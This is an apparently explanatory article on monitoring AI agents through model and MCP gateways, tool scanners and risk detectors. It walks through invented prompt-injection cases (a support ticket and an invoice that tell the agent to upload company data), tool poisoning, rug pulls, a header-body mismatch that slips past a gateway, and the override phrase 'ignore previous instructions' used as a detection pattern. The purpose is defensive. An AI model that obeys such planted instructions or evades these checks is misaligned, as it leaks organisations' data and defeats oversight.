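# Detecting risky AI agent behaviour with gateways, agent-security tools and Model Context Protocol monitoring

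## Agents, tools and the points where their actions are recorded

An AI agent is software in which a language model repeatedly chooses actions for tools to carry out. The tools may read files, query a database, send email or run commands on a computer, so an agent can do damage that a program that only returns text cannot. Organisations try to detect harmful or unauthorised actions by recording what passes between the agent, the model and the tools, then comparing it with records they already keep, such as login histories and activity logs from employees' machines. Some of this recording happens in AI gateways, which are proxies that forward and log AI traffic and may block some of it. Many gateways handle the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open protocol that agents use to discover and call external tools and data sources.

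### The agent loop

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the cycle for Codex CLI, an OpenAI coding agent that runs on the user's own machine. The program combines the user's request with standing instructions and a list of available tools, and sends them to the model as a prompt. The model returns either a final answer or a request for a tool call, for example to list the files in a folder. If it returns a tool call, the program runs the tool, adds the output to the prompt and queries the model again, until it returns a final answer.

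Anthropic gives an example in its documentation for a kit for building agents on the same loop as its coding agent Claude Code. A user types a request to fix the failing tests in one file. The model requests a test run, which shows three failures. It then requests the contents of two files, an edit and a second test run, which passes, and writes a one-line report. The user's one sentence has led to five tool calls, and Bolin notes that an agent could make hundreds before it answers. A session is all the model exchanges and actions in one run on one task.

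To use a tool, the model produces text that names the tool and gives arguments, and the program around the model may or may not act on that text. The call that runs can also differ from the one the model proposed. For example, Anthropic's kit lets developers insert hooks, pieces of their own code that run before a tool does and can change or block the call. A record of what the model proposed therefore does not prove what happened on the machine. When a rule denies a call, the model receives a rejection message and typically tries another approach or reports that it could not proceed, so a variant of the blocked call may well follow soon after.

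With each new query, Codex also resends the conversation so far, including earlier tool calls and their output. When the text grows too long, Codex replaces it with a shorter version. A sentence in a document that the agent opened early on can therefore still influence the model many calls later.

### How MCP connects an agent to tools

The project behind the protocol, Model Context Protocol (2026), reported close to half a billion downloads a month for its main software kits when it released the July 2026 revision, which made every request self-contained. (Downloads include automated installations, so the number is no count of working agents.)

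MCP has three roles. The host is the application that the user works in, such as a coding agent or a desktop assistant, and the loop runs inside it. The MCP server is a program that offers tools. The host creates a separate component, called a client, to handle its connection to each server. The Model Context Protocol architecture documentation states as a design principle that a server should not be able to read the whole conversation or see into other servers; the full history stays with the host. A server's own log will therefore usually show what the agent requested but not why.

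Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) defines the two main messages, `tools/list` and `tools/call`. When the client sends `tools/list`, the server returns each tool's name, a description in ordinary language and a schema of the arguments the tool accepts. The host merges the lists from all its servers into one registry for the model, as the Model Context Protocol architecture overview explains. When the model picks a tool, the host finds the server that offers it, and the client sends that server `tools/call` with the tool's name and arguments. In the specification's example, the client calls `get_weather` for New York and receives a short text with the temperature and sky conditions. That text goes back into the prompt.

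A server's list of tools may change, and the server can notify clients when it does. The server may also attach annotations about how a tool behaves, which clients must treat as untrusted unless they trust the server. Under the specification, a person "should" always be able to refuse a tool call, but this is not mandatory. The developer Simon Willison argues that confirmation fatigue is real and that asking people to click OK every few steps will not make agents safe.

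Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) describes two standard ways to send the messages. A local server runs on the same machine as the agent. The client starts it as a subprocess, and the two exchange lines of text over standard input and output, the channels that an operating system gives every program. These messages cross no network. A server that gives a desktop assistant access to the user's files typically works this way. With a remote server, the client sends each message as an HTTP request to a single web address. The error-tracking company Sentry offers a remote server on its own platform. Developers may also write custom transports, provided they keep the message format.

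### Built-in tools

An agent also has built-in tools, which are part of the agent program itself and don't use MCP. Anthropic says the built-in tools in its agent kit can read, write and edit files, run commands and search the web. It lists MCP separately as a way to connect more tools and data.

Different kinds of tools look much alike to the model. Bolin shows part of the tool list that Codex sends to the model: a shell tool that starts processes on the user's machine, a tool for updating the agent's plan, a web search provided by OpenAI, and a weather tool from an MCP server that the user has configured. This one list covers actions on the user's machine, at the model provider and on any server the user has added. Codex runs its shell tool in a sandbox that limits file and network access, but the sandbox does not cover MCP tools, so their servers have to enforce their own limits.

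An agent with a shell often has two ways to do the same thing. For example, it can query a database through an MCP server, or it can run the database's command-line program, which doesn't involve an MCP call.

### The recording points

An organisation can record what an agent does, or what it is about to use, at seven points.

| Recording point | Where it sits | What it records |
|---|---|---|
| Model gateway | Between the agent and the language model | Prompts, tool lists and the model's replies, including the tool calls it proposes |
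| MCP gateway | Between the agent and its MCP servers | `tools/list` and `tools/call` messages, with arguments and results |
| Tool scanner | Outside the path of calls, before the agent uses a server | Server code, tool names and descriptions as they stood at the time of the scan |
| Identity provider | Where people and programs log in | Who or what obtained which credential, when, and with what permissions |
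| Device sensor | On the machine where the agent runs | Processes, file access, network connections, configuration |
| Trace collector | A service to which programs report their steps | The steps of one request through several systems, under a shared identifier |
| Log of the system acted upon | In the database, mail server or other target | The operations that this system carried out, and for which account |

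Vendors sell both MCP gateways and tool scanners as MCP security products, though they do different jobs. Agent Security Index's *MCP gateway vs MCP scanner* (2026), a directory page based on product listings, not tests, lists thirteen gateways, four scanners and one product that does both. A scanner doesn't block anything at run time, and people can still misuse a server that has passed a scan. A gateway acts on each call that reaches it, but can't act on calls that don't. A recording point's coverage is the share of relevant agent actions that cross it. For the same agent over the same period, coverage can be nearly complete at one point and close to zero at another.

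### What makes an action risky

An agent's action is risky when it may harm the organisation or other people, or when it goes beyond what anyone authorised. The cause may be hostile content that steers the agent, the agent's own error or overreach, or a user who misuses it.

Hostile content works because a model receives instructions and data in one stream of text and cannot reliably tell them apart. In a prompt injection, an attacker hides instructions in content that the agent reads, and the agent follows them. The US Center for AI Standards and Innovation, in work published by NIST, treats agent hijacking as a form of prompt injection. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (Errico, Ngiam and Sojan, 2025) gives the invented example of a support ticket in which a customer writes that, to debug the problem, the agent must pull all the logs from every data warehouse it can access, zip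 them and upload them to a given web address. An agent that works through tickets may take this for part of the job. Such theft requires what the paper calls the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to send data out. One of the paper's three authors works for a company that sells an MCP gateway, but the attack it describes requires only the agent's ordinary loop.

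Tool poisoning places malicious instructions in a tool's description or other metadata. Yang, Zheng and colleagues (2026) explain in *Securing the AI Agent* that the model takes in the description as trusted context, so whoever writes it can steer the model. A currency converter's description could include an instruction to first read a file of passwords and pass its contents along as an argument. Because this text arrives with the tool list, it reaches the model before any call and can affect how the model uses other tools. A supplier can also alter a server after users have come to trust it, which Errico and colleagues call a rug pull. A malicious server may instead do its harm in its own code, in which case the agent's call looks ordinary.

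However, models may take harmful actions "even in the absence of adversarial inputs", according to NIST's announcement of a request for information on agent security. The full request, in the Federal Register (2026), gives the example of specification gaming, in which a model satisfies the letter of its goal in a way its designers did not intend. Anthropic distinguishes overeager behaviour from honest mistakes, such as treating a shared resource as a test copy or a colleague's branch as the agent's own. Errico and colleagues describe agents that disclose secrets while debugging, or that look for another path when a rule blocks them. Every call an agent makes in these cases may be well formed and within policy.

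A user can also misuse an agent on purpose, for example by having it collect customer records to take to a new employer. Anthropic's list of four causes (the two above, plus prompt injection and a misaligned model) doesn't include this, and neither does Errico and colleagues' list of three adversaries, although the resulting tool calls may be the same as in the cases they list.

Anthropic says the defence is to block the action, whichever of the four causes is behind it. That is reasonable for a plainly bad call. For an ambiguous call, the cause matters more, because the evidence for each cause is in a different place. An injection leaves text in a document or a tool description. Misuse often shows in the user's request. An agent's error may leave no suspicious text, only a difference between what the user wanted and what the agent did.

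Many calls can be safe or harmful depending on the context. Sending the supplier list to an outside address is routine if the finance director has told the agent to send it to the auditors, but it is a leak if the task was to summarise invoices. Deleting a branch is routine cleanup if the agent created it an hour earlier. The text of the call can be identical in the safe and harmful cases, so a person, rule or model judging it also needs information about the task, who requested it and what the agent had read by then.

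### An invoice with a hidden instruction

In a hypothetical case, an employee in the accounts department has an agent on a laptop. The agent can reach the company's invoices through an MCP server and has a built-in shell.

1. The employee asks the agent to summarise last month's invoices.
2. The agent calls a tool on the MCP server and reads the invoices.
3. One invoice contains, in white letters on a white background, an instruction to send the company's supplier list to an outside web address.
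4. The model, with that sentence now in its prompt, proposes a shell command that would upload the list.
5. The agent program runs the command, and the supplier list goes to the outside address.

### How to read a detection score

Suppose that an organisation tests a detector on 1,000 tool calls, 20 of them risky, with these results (also invented):

| | Alarm | No alarm | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
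| Risky calls | 16 | 4 | 20 |
| Harmless calls | 49 | 931 | 980 |
| Total | 65 | 935 | 1,000 |

Recall is the share of risky calls that set off an alarm, here 16 of 20, or 80%. The false positive rate is the share of harmless calls that set one off, here 49 of 980, or 5%. Precision is the share of alarms that were set off by risky calls, here 16 of 65, or about 25%.

Precision depends heavily on how rare risky calls are. A detector with 80% recall and a 5% false positive rate has 94% precision when tested on 500 risky and 500 harmless calls. With 20 risky calls among 100,000, the same detector's precision falls to about 0.3%, or one real problem in some 300 alarms. High precision on a test set that is half attacks is therefore a poor guide to the workload in an office where attacks are rare.

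False alarm rates per call and per session are not comparable. If a detector wrongly flags 5% of harmless calls and its errors are independent, the probability of at least one false alarm in a session of forty harmless calls is 1 − 0.95⁴⁰, or about 87%. At 1% per call, it is still 33%. Real errors tend to cluster, which lowers these numbers somewhat.

Many detectors give a score instead of a yes or no, and their operators choose the threshold above which a score triggers an alarm. A lower threshold catches more risky calls but also flags more harmless ones. Plotting recall against the false positive rate at every threshold gives the receiver operating characteristic curve, and AUROC is the area under it. AUROC equals the probability that a randomly chosen risky call scores higher than a randomly chosen harmless one, with ties counting as half. A value of 0.5 is no better than chance, and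 1 means every risky call scores above every harmless one. AUROC covers all thresholds, including many that nobody would use, so a detector with an AUROC of 0.95 can still miss most risky calls when the threshold is high enough to flag only one in a thousand harmless calls.

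## What a gateway can and cannot see by design

What a gateway can record depends on which messages reach it and whether it can decrypt them. The protocols and network layout determine both, so an organisation can work them out before testing any detector.

### Where the encryption ends

Agents normally reach a model provider or a remote MCP server over HTTPS, which uses the TLS protocol to encrypt everything sent between the two ends of a connection. A proxy that only relays the connection can usually log which host the agent contacted, when, and how much data passed, but it can't read the prompt. To read the content, the gateway has to terminate TLS, which means acting as one end of the agent's encrypted connection. It then decrypts each message, records it and sends it to the real destination over a second encrypted connection.

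An organisation can let a gateway read an agent's encrypted traffic in two ways. The first is to replace the provider's address in the agent's settings with the gateway's, so that the agent opens its encrypted connection to the gateway. This works only where the organisation controls the settings and nobody changes them back. The second is to intercept the traffic by installing the organisation's own root certificate on employees' machines, so that they accept a proxy that presents certificates in the provider's name. Interception also covers agents that nobody has configured to use the gateway, but it fails on machines without the root certificate and with programs that accept only the provider's own certificate.

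Either way, the gateway handles prompts, files and often credentials in readable form, which makes a flaw in gateway software costly.

### What each gateway records

| Field | Model gateway | MCP gateway |
|---|---|---|
| User's request and standing instructions | Yes, in the prompt | No |
| Tool definitions | Every tool offered to the model, built-in tools included | Only tools of the servers behind the gateway |
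| Calls the model proposes | Yes, with arguments | No |
| Calls the agent program sends | No | Those to servers behind the gateway, with arguments |
| Tool output | Once the agent program returns it to the model | As the server returned it |
| Model's final answer | Yes | No |

The agent program sends its full tool list with the prompt, so a model gateway logs the definitions of a shell and a file editor as well as those of the MCP tools. The full text of each call the model proposes also passes through the gateway before the agent program receives it, whether the call is a shell command or a request to an MCP server on the user's own laptop. A gateway that holds the reply until it has checked it can block either kind of call.

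The model gateway receives a tool's output only when the agent program sends it with the next query, perhaps in shortened form. The output of the last call may never arrive if the user closes the program. Hooks can change a call before it runs, so the log may contain the original command instead of the one that ran. Some model interfaces let the program refer to an earlier exchange by an identifier instead of resending it, so a logged request may hold only the newest part of the conversation. Some providers return the model's reasoning only as a summary or in encrypted form.

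A gateway also has a limited view of scripts. If an agent runs `python cleanup.py`, the log contains that command and whatever the script prints. It also contains the script's text if the agent wrote the script earlier in the session, because the text was an argument of an earlier call. If a colleague wrote the script, the gateway has no copy unless the agent opened the file first.

An MCP gateway acts as a server to the agent and a client to the real servers. It can record everything in the `tools/list` and `tools/call` exchanges, including tool descriptions and error messages. Servers may also offer ready-made prompts and data that clients read by address, and requests for these (`prompts/get` and `resources/read`) pass through the gateway too. A log entry for a call shows that the agent program actually sent it, which a model gateway's log can't show. But like a server's own log, the entry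 usually doesn't show why the agent made the call.

### What stays off-route

An MCP gateway can't intercept messages between an agent and a local MCP server because, under the protocol, those messages don't cross a network. Model Context Protocol also advises developers to take a local server's credentials from the machine's environment instead of using the authorisation framework for HTTP, so a gateway can't discover the server from login exchanges either. An organisation can monitor these messages by having the agent start a small relay program that records them and passes them to the real server, or by moving the server to a remote host behind the gateway. Both options require control over the agent's configuration.

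Shell commands and direct API calls bypass the MCP gateway because they don't use MCP. Suppose an agent writes a script that takes a key from a settings file and calls a cloud provider's API. The model gateway logs the script and its printed output, but the script's requests go straight to the cloud provider. If the agent schedules the script to run every night, those runs don't involve a model and leave nothing in either gateway's log.

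When an agent uses a model running on the same machine, its prompts never leave that machine and so don't pass through the model gateway. An MCP gateway still records the agent's calls to the remote servers behind it, but there are no recorded prompts to compare them with.

Employees may also log in to a provider with a personal account, often from a program still set to the provider's own address rather than the gateway's. An intercepting proxy may catch this on a company laptop, but traffic from a phone or home computer doesn't pass through the company's network.

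If a provider hosts the agent, the agent loop and the model queries run on the provider's machines, so the organisation can record the agent's activity only where it reaches the organisation's own systems. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) describes a research preview of MCP tunnels, which connect Claude to MCP servers inside a private network without a public endpoint or inbound firewall rules. The organisation's MCP gateway can record the calls if the tunnel ends in front of it, but if the tunnel leads directly to the server, the calls bypass the gateway even though they reach the organisation's systems.

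Finally, a permitted call can have effects that no gateway records. A call to a tool named `close_month` might lead the server to change a ledger and send forty emails, while the gateway logs only the request and the result "done". Results can also arrive later. Model Context Protocol (2026), which announces the release candidate of the July 2026 revision, explains that under an extension called Tasks, a server may answer a call with a handle for a long-running job, and the client asks about the job later. A gateway then has to match the later answer to the original call.

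### The invoice example at both gateways

Suppose the employee's agent sends its model queries through a model gateway, and the invoice server is remote and behind an MCP gateway.

| Step | Model gateway | MCP gateway |
|---|---|---|
| 1. The employee asks for a summary | Seen, in the first prompt | Unseen |
| 2. The agent reads the invoices | Seen, as a proposed call and then as output in the next prompt | Seen, as a call and its result |
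| 3. One invoice contains the hidden instruction | Seen, as text | Seen, as text |
| 4. The model proposes the upload command | Seen | Unseen |
| 5. The command runs and the list leaves | Partly seen, if the command's output returns to the model | Unseen |

In step 3, both gateways record the sentence, provided the server extracts the invoice's text. White letters on a white background become ordinary characters when a program extracts them, so nothing in the log marks the sentence as hidden. (If the server returns a picture of the page, the gateways record the picture and would have to read it.)

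The MCP gateway records the malicious sentence and one ordinary request for invoices, but none of the theft. If the invoice server ran on the laptop, the MCP gateway would record none of the five steps. Of the two gateways, only the model gateway could stop the upload, at step 4. But the supplier list itself may never appear in the model traffic, because the command only has to name the file and the shell reads the contents from disk. In that case, a filter that searches the traffic for suppliers' names would find nothing.

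### One request under two revisions of MCP

The July 2026 revision of MCP, which bears the date 2026-07-28, changes what a gateway can read from a single message. Under the previous revision, 2025-11-25, a client first sent an `initialize` request with its name, version and capabilities. The server could then assign a session identifier, which the client had to repeat on every later request. The agent's request for invoices might look like this:

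```http
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Content-Type: application/json
MCP-Protocol-Version: 2025-11-25
Mcp-Session-Id: 1868a90c-3a3f-4f5b

{"jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 2, "method": "tools/call",
 "params": {"name": "get_invoices",
            "arguments": {"month": "2026-09"}}}
```

Under 2026-07-28 there is no `initialize` request and no session identifier, and the same call looks like this:

```http
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
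Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: get_invoices
Content-Type: application/json
MCP-Protocol-Version: 2026-07-28

{"jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 2, "method": "tools/call",
 "params": {"name": "get_invoices",
            "arguments": {"month": "2026-09"},
            "_meta": {
              "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
              "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientInfo":
                {"name": "accounts-agent", "version": "1.0"},
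              "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {}}}}
```

The lines above the blank one are HTTP headers, and the rest is the body. The method and the tool's name now appear in both. The client also repeats, in each request's `_meta`, information it used to send only once, at the start, so a gateway can interpret any request without having recorded an earlier one.

**The session identifier.** Under the old revision, a gateway could group calls that carried the same session identifier. This grouping was rough because each identifier covered only one client's connection with one server. An agent that used three servers could have three identifiers, and none of them marked where the user's task began or ended. Without the identifier, a gateway has to group calls by access token, network address and time, or by trace-context fields where programs fill them in. It can't group them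 reliably by connection, because Model Context Protocol allows clients to mix unrelated requests on one connection.

Some applications provide a partial replacement. A server that needs to keep state between calls can return a handle, such as a `basket_id`, which the model passes back as an argument in later calls. A gateway can log the handle and use it to link those calls. The security company Akamai lists the end of protocol-level session hijacking as one of the revision's benefits, but warns that developers are now responsible for protecting that state.

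The method and name headers let a gateway count, route or block calls by tool without parsing the body. Körbächer (2026), in *A platform team's guide to MCP 7-28*, gives the example of a security team that wants at most ten `execute_sql` calls per customer per minute, and none in a certain region from test machines. Previously the gateway had to decrypt the traffic, parse the body and find the region among the arguments. Under the new revision, a server can mark an argument, such as the region, to be copied into a separate header, so the gateway can apply the rule using only the headers. It still has to terminate TLS, because HTTPS encrypts headers along with the body.

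The headers also give a gateway little information for judging risk. Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026) gives an example with the same `execute_sql` tool, in which the server has marked only the region, so the client copies the region into a header and leaves the SQL query in the body. A gateway that reads only headers could not tell a query that lists users from one that deletes them. Header values with non-ASCII characters also arrive in Base64, so the gateway must decode them before applying its rules. Körbächer warns that a rule for the region São Paulo would otherwise silently fail to match.

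A client might write `get_invoices` as the tool name in the header and `delete_invoices` in the body, so that a gateway approves the first and the server runs the second. Any server that processes the body must therefore compare the two and reject a mismatch with HTTP status 400 and error code -32020. A mismatch can also be accidental, as when a client with an outdated tool definition leaves out a required header. The specification advises such a client to fetch the tool list again and retry.

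This protection depends on the server, because a malicious or faulty one can skip the comparison. A gateway that needs a reliable log should therefore read the body and make the comparison itself. Older requests are another weakness. According to pgEdge's *mcp spec compliance*, a page about the database company's own MCP server, the server accepts both old and new requests but checks headers only on the new ones. A client could send an old-style request with a harmless tool name in a header that the server ignores. The specification says that gateways enforcing policy on these headers should check the protocol version and reject older requests. Körbächer would also allow a gateway to send older requests to a path that inspects the body instead.

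Körbächer's sample configuration leaves a gap, though he calls its version rule illustrative. It checks the version on the route for European regions, but a request without the region header falls through to a default route that has no such check. A prompt injection doesn't need a mismatch between header and body, because the hijacked agent sends a request in which both name the harmful tool.

**Client information.** Clients now send their name and version with each request, instead of just once. This helps with counting which agent programs are in use and finding faults. But the field is optional and the protocol does not verify it, so any program can call itself `accounts-agent`. The Model Context Protocol specification advises against relying on this field, or on a server's self-reported name, for security decisions. An access token is better evidence of who is calling, though whether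 it identifies the agent as well as the user depends on how the organisation issues it.

**Cacheable tool lists.** Every tool list now comes with `ttlMs`, which sets how many milliseconds a client may treat the list as fresh, and `cacheScope`, which determines whether different users may share a stored copy. In an example in Model Context Protocol's *Caching* (2026), a client reuses a list for five minutes without asking the server again. An MCP gateway may therefore log a tool call with no recent `tools/list` before it, and the server may have changed the tool's description since the client fetched the list. An investigator needs the model gateway's record of the prompt to learn which description the model had.

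Körbächer points out that a shared cache can also spread harm, because a poisoned description that a server marks as public can reach every client until the cached copy expires. But a gateway that stores the list can compare it with the next version and report any change. The revision makes this easier by advising servers to return tools in a fixed order. How often caching will matter depends on how servers set it. Model Context Protocol's *Caching hints*, from the Python kit's documentation, gives a default cache time of zero milliseconds and no sharing between users, while pgEdge marks its lists as public.

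**Multi round-trip requests.** Sometimes a server needs to ask the user a question, such as "Delete 3 files?", before it can finish a call. Under the old revision, the server could send its own request to the client over an open stream. Now it replies to the original call with a result of type `input_required`, which contains the question. The client gets the user's answer and resends the call with it attached, so a gateway can link each question to the call that prompted it.

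Under Model Context Protocol's *Multi Round-Trip Requests*, one deletion can appear in the log as two `tools/call` requests. The second must have a new request number, so a gateway that counts requests would count the deletion twice, and a detector that treats the first reply as success would record the deletion too early. The server may include a `requestState` string in its first reply, which the client returns unchanged in the second request. A gateway can use this string to match the two requests, but may not be able to read its contents because the server may encrypt it. A call may also be repeated because the connection broke before a result arrived. The client then has to send the call again under a new number, even though the first attempt may already have taken effect.

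The Logging feature lets MCP servers send log messages to the client through the protocol, where an MCP gateway can record them. Model Context Protocol's *Logging* (2026) deprecates the feature but keeps it in the specification for at least twelve months. During that time, a server may send log messages only if the client's request asks for them. The recommended replacements are standard error (a text output for diagnostics) for local servers, and OpenTelemetry, an open standard for collecting traces and logs. Both take the messages out of the gateway's path, and Model Context Protocol's documentation for its Python kit confirms that nothing within the protocol replaces them. Monitoring therefore loses some context about errors, but probably little evidence of theft, since a malicious server would be unlikely to log its own.

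### How far the revision has spread

Software support for the revision came quickly. On release day, the Model Context Protocol project announced support in its main SDKs for TypeScript, Python, Go and C#, with Rust in beta. Cloudflare reported support in its agent SDK from the first day, and Amazon in its Bedrock AgentCore service. The project later announced full support in the official Ruby SDK (Model Context Protocol, 2026). Anthropic said on release day only that it was rolling out support across its Claude products.

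An agent may not use the new revision even if its kit supports it. Developers using the TypeScript kit have to opt in, according to Model Context Protocol's *Supporting protocol revision 2026-07-28*. Model Context Protocol's documentation for the C# kit describes a client that prefers the new revision but can fall back to the old `initialize` exchange. The monthly download totals combine all versions of the kits, and none of these announcements gives the share of working clients or servers that use the new revision. An organisation that installs an MCP gateway should therefore expect both kinds of request and measure the mix in its own traffic.

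### Coverage limits recall

Let *q* be the share of risky actions that cross the gateway in readable form, and *r* the detector's recall on those. Out of *N* risky actions, *qN* cross the gateway and *r* × *qN* set off an alarm. The rest of the *N* actions set off none. Dividing the alarms on risky actions by all risky actions gives:

overall recall = (*r* × *qN*) / *N* = *q* × *r*

If 60% of risky actions cross the gateway (*q* = 0.60) and the detector catches 90% of those (*r* = 0.90), overall recall is 0.54. Of 100 risky actions, 54 set off an alarm, the detector misses 6, and the other 40 bypass the gateway and leave no entry in its log. A perfect detector would raise overall recall only to 0.60, whereas raising *q* to 0.90 with the same detector would bring it to 0.81.

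In the formula, *q* is the share of risky actions that cross the gateway, which may be far lower than the share of all actions that do. Suppose that agents carry out 10,000 actions in a month and 9,500 of them, or 95%, cross the gateway. If 40 of the 100 risky actions are among the 500 that don't cross, *q* is only 0.60. Such a gap is plausible, because a user who means to misuse an agent can choose an unmonitored route, and an agent may try the shell after a gateway has blocked a tool. An organisation can take *r* from a vendor's test only if the risky actions in the test resemble those that cross its own gateway.

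If 60% of risky actions cross the model gateway and 30% cross the MCP gateway, between 60% and 90% cross at least one, depending on how many cross both. The total will be near the lower end if the same agents use both gateways, because most of their MCP calls also appear in the model traffic.

A gateway can't measure *q*, the share of risky actions that pass through it, from its own log. Suppose two companies have identical logs, each containing 60 risky actions. In the first, agents took no other risky actions, so *q* is 1. In the second, they took 40 more by routes that bypass the gateway, so *q* is 0.60. Even counting the 60 takes work, because the log marks only the 54 that set off alarms, and someone has to find the other 6 among the calls that didn't.

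If an agent's model queries pass through a model gateway, the organisation can compare the tool calls proposed there with the MCP gateway's log and estimate how many went instead to the shell or to local servers. An agent that uses a local model and only local tools appears in neither log, so the organisation needs other evidence to count its actions, such as records from the device or from the systems on which the agent acted.

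## How tools decide that an action is risky

A detector may check a tool before any agent uses it, or it may check a single call, a sequence of calls, or where data is going. Each type of check needs different information.

| Object | Inputs | Decision procedure | Possible verdicts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Server or tool | Name, description and argument schema; sometimes source code or a test run | Search the definition for attacks and compare it with the last approved version | Allow, record a warning, ask a person to review it, block |
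| Single call | Tool name, arguments and the agent's identity; sometimes the user's request | Check lists and rules, then the text of the call and its result | Allow, record, ask a person, block |
| Sequence of calls | Earlier calls and results in the session, and what the task permits | Note what kinds of data the agent has read, and test each new call against that | Allow, record, ask a person or block the next call |
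| Destination of data | Address or account, and the kind of data | Compare with the approved recipients for that kind of data | Allow, record, ask a person, block, or remove the sensitive part |

A call to an approved tool can still be unsafe. *ToolGuardian* (Ravindran and Deochake, 2026) gives the example of network access, which is appropriate for a weather query but may be unsafe once the agent has read sensitive local data. The mildest verdict after "allow" is "record", which lets the call go ahead so that an analyst may review it later. Recording doesn't interrupt anyone's work, but if the call uploads data, a later review can't undo the upload.

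### Lists and permission rules

The simplest method compares the tool's name with a list. An allowlist names the tools that an agent may call, and the gateway blocks all others. A denylist names only the tools to block. Permission rules add conditions. For example, a rule may let an agent run `execute_sql` on a test database but require a person's approval for the live one.

*AI Agent Gateway* (Pogorelec, 2026) describes how an open-source gateway from the company Tuskira applies such a list. In each request, the agent names a profile and includes its key for the gateway. If the key is valid, the gateway looks up whether that profile permits the tool. If the profile doesn't permit it, the gateway logs the attempt and returns an error without forwarding the request to the server. Otherwise, the gateway attaches the real credential, such as a GitHub token, and forwards the call, so the agent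 never holds the credential. The gateway also hides forbidden tools from the agent, but it still checks each call, so a prompt injection that names a hidden tool fails. If a key isn't tied to a profile, the gateway by default lets the caller choose one, so a thief with that key can request any profile.

Lists that identify tools by name alone are unreliable. According to the Model Context Protocol, when a client or proxy combines tools from several servers, names may collide; two servers may each offer a tool called `search`, for example. The protocol recommends telling such tools apart, for instance by adding a server identifier to the name. The server's self-reported name is unsuitable as that identifier because two servers can report the same one.

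Lists are predictable and easy to audit, but a list that lets an agent send email allows any email unless further rules restrict the recipients or content.

### Tool annotations

An MCP server can annotate each tool with four yes-or-no hints. Model Context Protocol (2026) reviews these hints and gives their defaults and the client behaviour each could support.

| Hint | Question it answers | Default | What a client might do |
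|---|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | Does the tool leave its environment unchanged? | No | Skip confirmation if yes |
| `destructiveHint` | If it makes changes, can they destroy something? | Yes | Warn the user first |
| `idempotentHint` | Is it safe to repeat the call with the same arguments? | No | Retry after a failure if yes |
| `openWorldHint` | Does it deal with outside parties or systems? | Yes | Check the output for untrusted content |

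By default, the Model Context Protocol treats a tool without annotations as one that may make changes, including destructive ones, and interact with external systems. Many servers omit the annotations, and clients differ in how strictly they apply these defaults.

The specification treats the hints as untrusted because their author may be an attacker, who could label a tool read-only and then use it to delete the user's files. When the protocol's developers reviewed the original proposal, its co-creator Justin Spahr-Summers asked how a client could use a flag that it can't trust, and another reviewer, Basil Hosmer, wanted clients to ignore annotations from untrusted servers. They settled on hints that each client weighs according to what it knows about the server. Model Context Protocol's Java documentation, *Record Class McpSchema.ToolAnnotations*, is stricter and tells clients never to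 base decisions about tool use on an untrusted server's annotations. But according to Model Context Protocol's review, most clients trust a server once the user installs it, so a user who installs a malicious server has usually accepted its hints too.

Hints can mislead even when they are set in good faith. Outreach's *Tool Annotations*, a sales-software company's documentation for its own MCP tools, describes read-only tools as safe to approve automatically. But stealing private data starts with reading it, and a client that approves every read automatically can only stop the theft when the data is being sent. Outreach also marks all its tools as open-world, meaning that they interact with external systems, because they contact its own backend. A client therefore can't use this hint to distinguish between Outreach's tools. The Model Context Protocol project acknowledges that "external" may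 mean outside the company network or merely outside the user's machine.

### Scans and fingerprints of tool definitions

A tool scanner searches a tool's definition for signs of tool poisoning. Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway* (2025), a draft specification from the company's Agent Governance Toolkit team, describes a scanner that looks for hidden text (such as invisible characters, comments or encoded passages), injected instructions in the description, suspicious fields in the argument schema, and references to tools on other servers. The scanner must also raise an alarm if a tool's name is within two single-character edits of the name of a tool on another server, since an attacker may imitate a trusted name. This rule will produce false alarms, because `get_user` and `set_user` are only one edit apart, and two legitimate servers may both offer a tool called `search`.

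To detect later changes to a tool, the scanner computes separate SHA-256 hashes of its description and argument schema. Each hash is a short string that in practice changes whenever the text does. The scanner recomputes both hashes when the tool loads again and reports a possible rug pull with critical severity if either differs. A corrected typo triggers the same alert as a new malicious instruction, so a person or another detector still has to read the new text.

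Microsoft's draft contradicts itself about how serious a changed tool description is. A second component, the drift detector, compares whole tool lists and rates a changed description as "info", the lowest of three levels. It rates a removed tool or a new required argument as critical. The same edit to a description can therefore produce both a critical alarm and an info notice. The critical rating makes more sense for tool poisoning, because an attacker needs to change only the description.

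Fingerprints have other weaknesses. If the drift detector has no earlier version to compare with, it accepts the current list as its baseline, so a tool that was malicious from the start passes. A server's code can also change while its description stays the same. *MCP-DPT* (Rostamzadeh, Narula and colleagues, 2026) illustrates this with a tool that passes approval on its declared behaviour and turns malicious only when it runs. False alarms are also possible because MCP lets a server show different tools to callers with different permissions. A drift detector that compares an administrator's list with a trainee's would report the tools missing from the trainee's list as critical removals.

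### Patterns, trained classifiers and language models as judges

A pattern describes the form of a piece of text, for example the groups of three, two and four digits in a US Social Security number. Microsoft's draft requires scanners to search tool results for markers that imitate a model's instruction format, commands such as "ignore previous instructions", credentials, personal data, and web addresses with sensitive-looking data in their parameters. If a result contains a key that starts with `sk-proj-`, the gateway can replace the key with `[REDACTED]`. Pattern matching is fast and consistent, but it can miss a key that has been hidden with simple encoding. It can also miss an instruction in an invoice that politely asks for a file to be sent somewhere and uses none of the stock phrases.

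**Trained text classifiers** learn from texts labelled as attacks or harmless. In one common design, a model converts a text into a list of numbers, called an embedding, so that texts with similar meanings get similar numbers. The classifier then turns the embedding into a score. It can recognise a rephrased attack that matches no pattern, but it tends to do worse on text unlike its training examples, and it usually gives no reason for the score that an analyst could check.

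**Language models as judges.** A program gives a language model the policy, the proposed call and any available context, and asks for a verdict with reasons. If the context includes the user's request, the model can assess whether the call fits the task, which pattern matching can't do. But verdicts may vary between runs, and an attacker's text can influence the judge as well as the agent. Leaving that text out protects the judge but removes evidence. Judging calls also adds to the cost of running the agent. In Ravindran and Deochake's experiment, each judgement took an average of about 2,750 tokens (short pieces of text) of input, so judging a session of 100 calls at that rate would take about 275,000.

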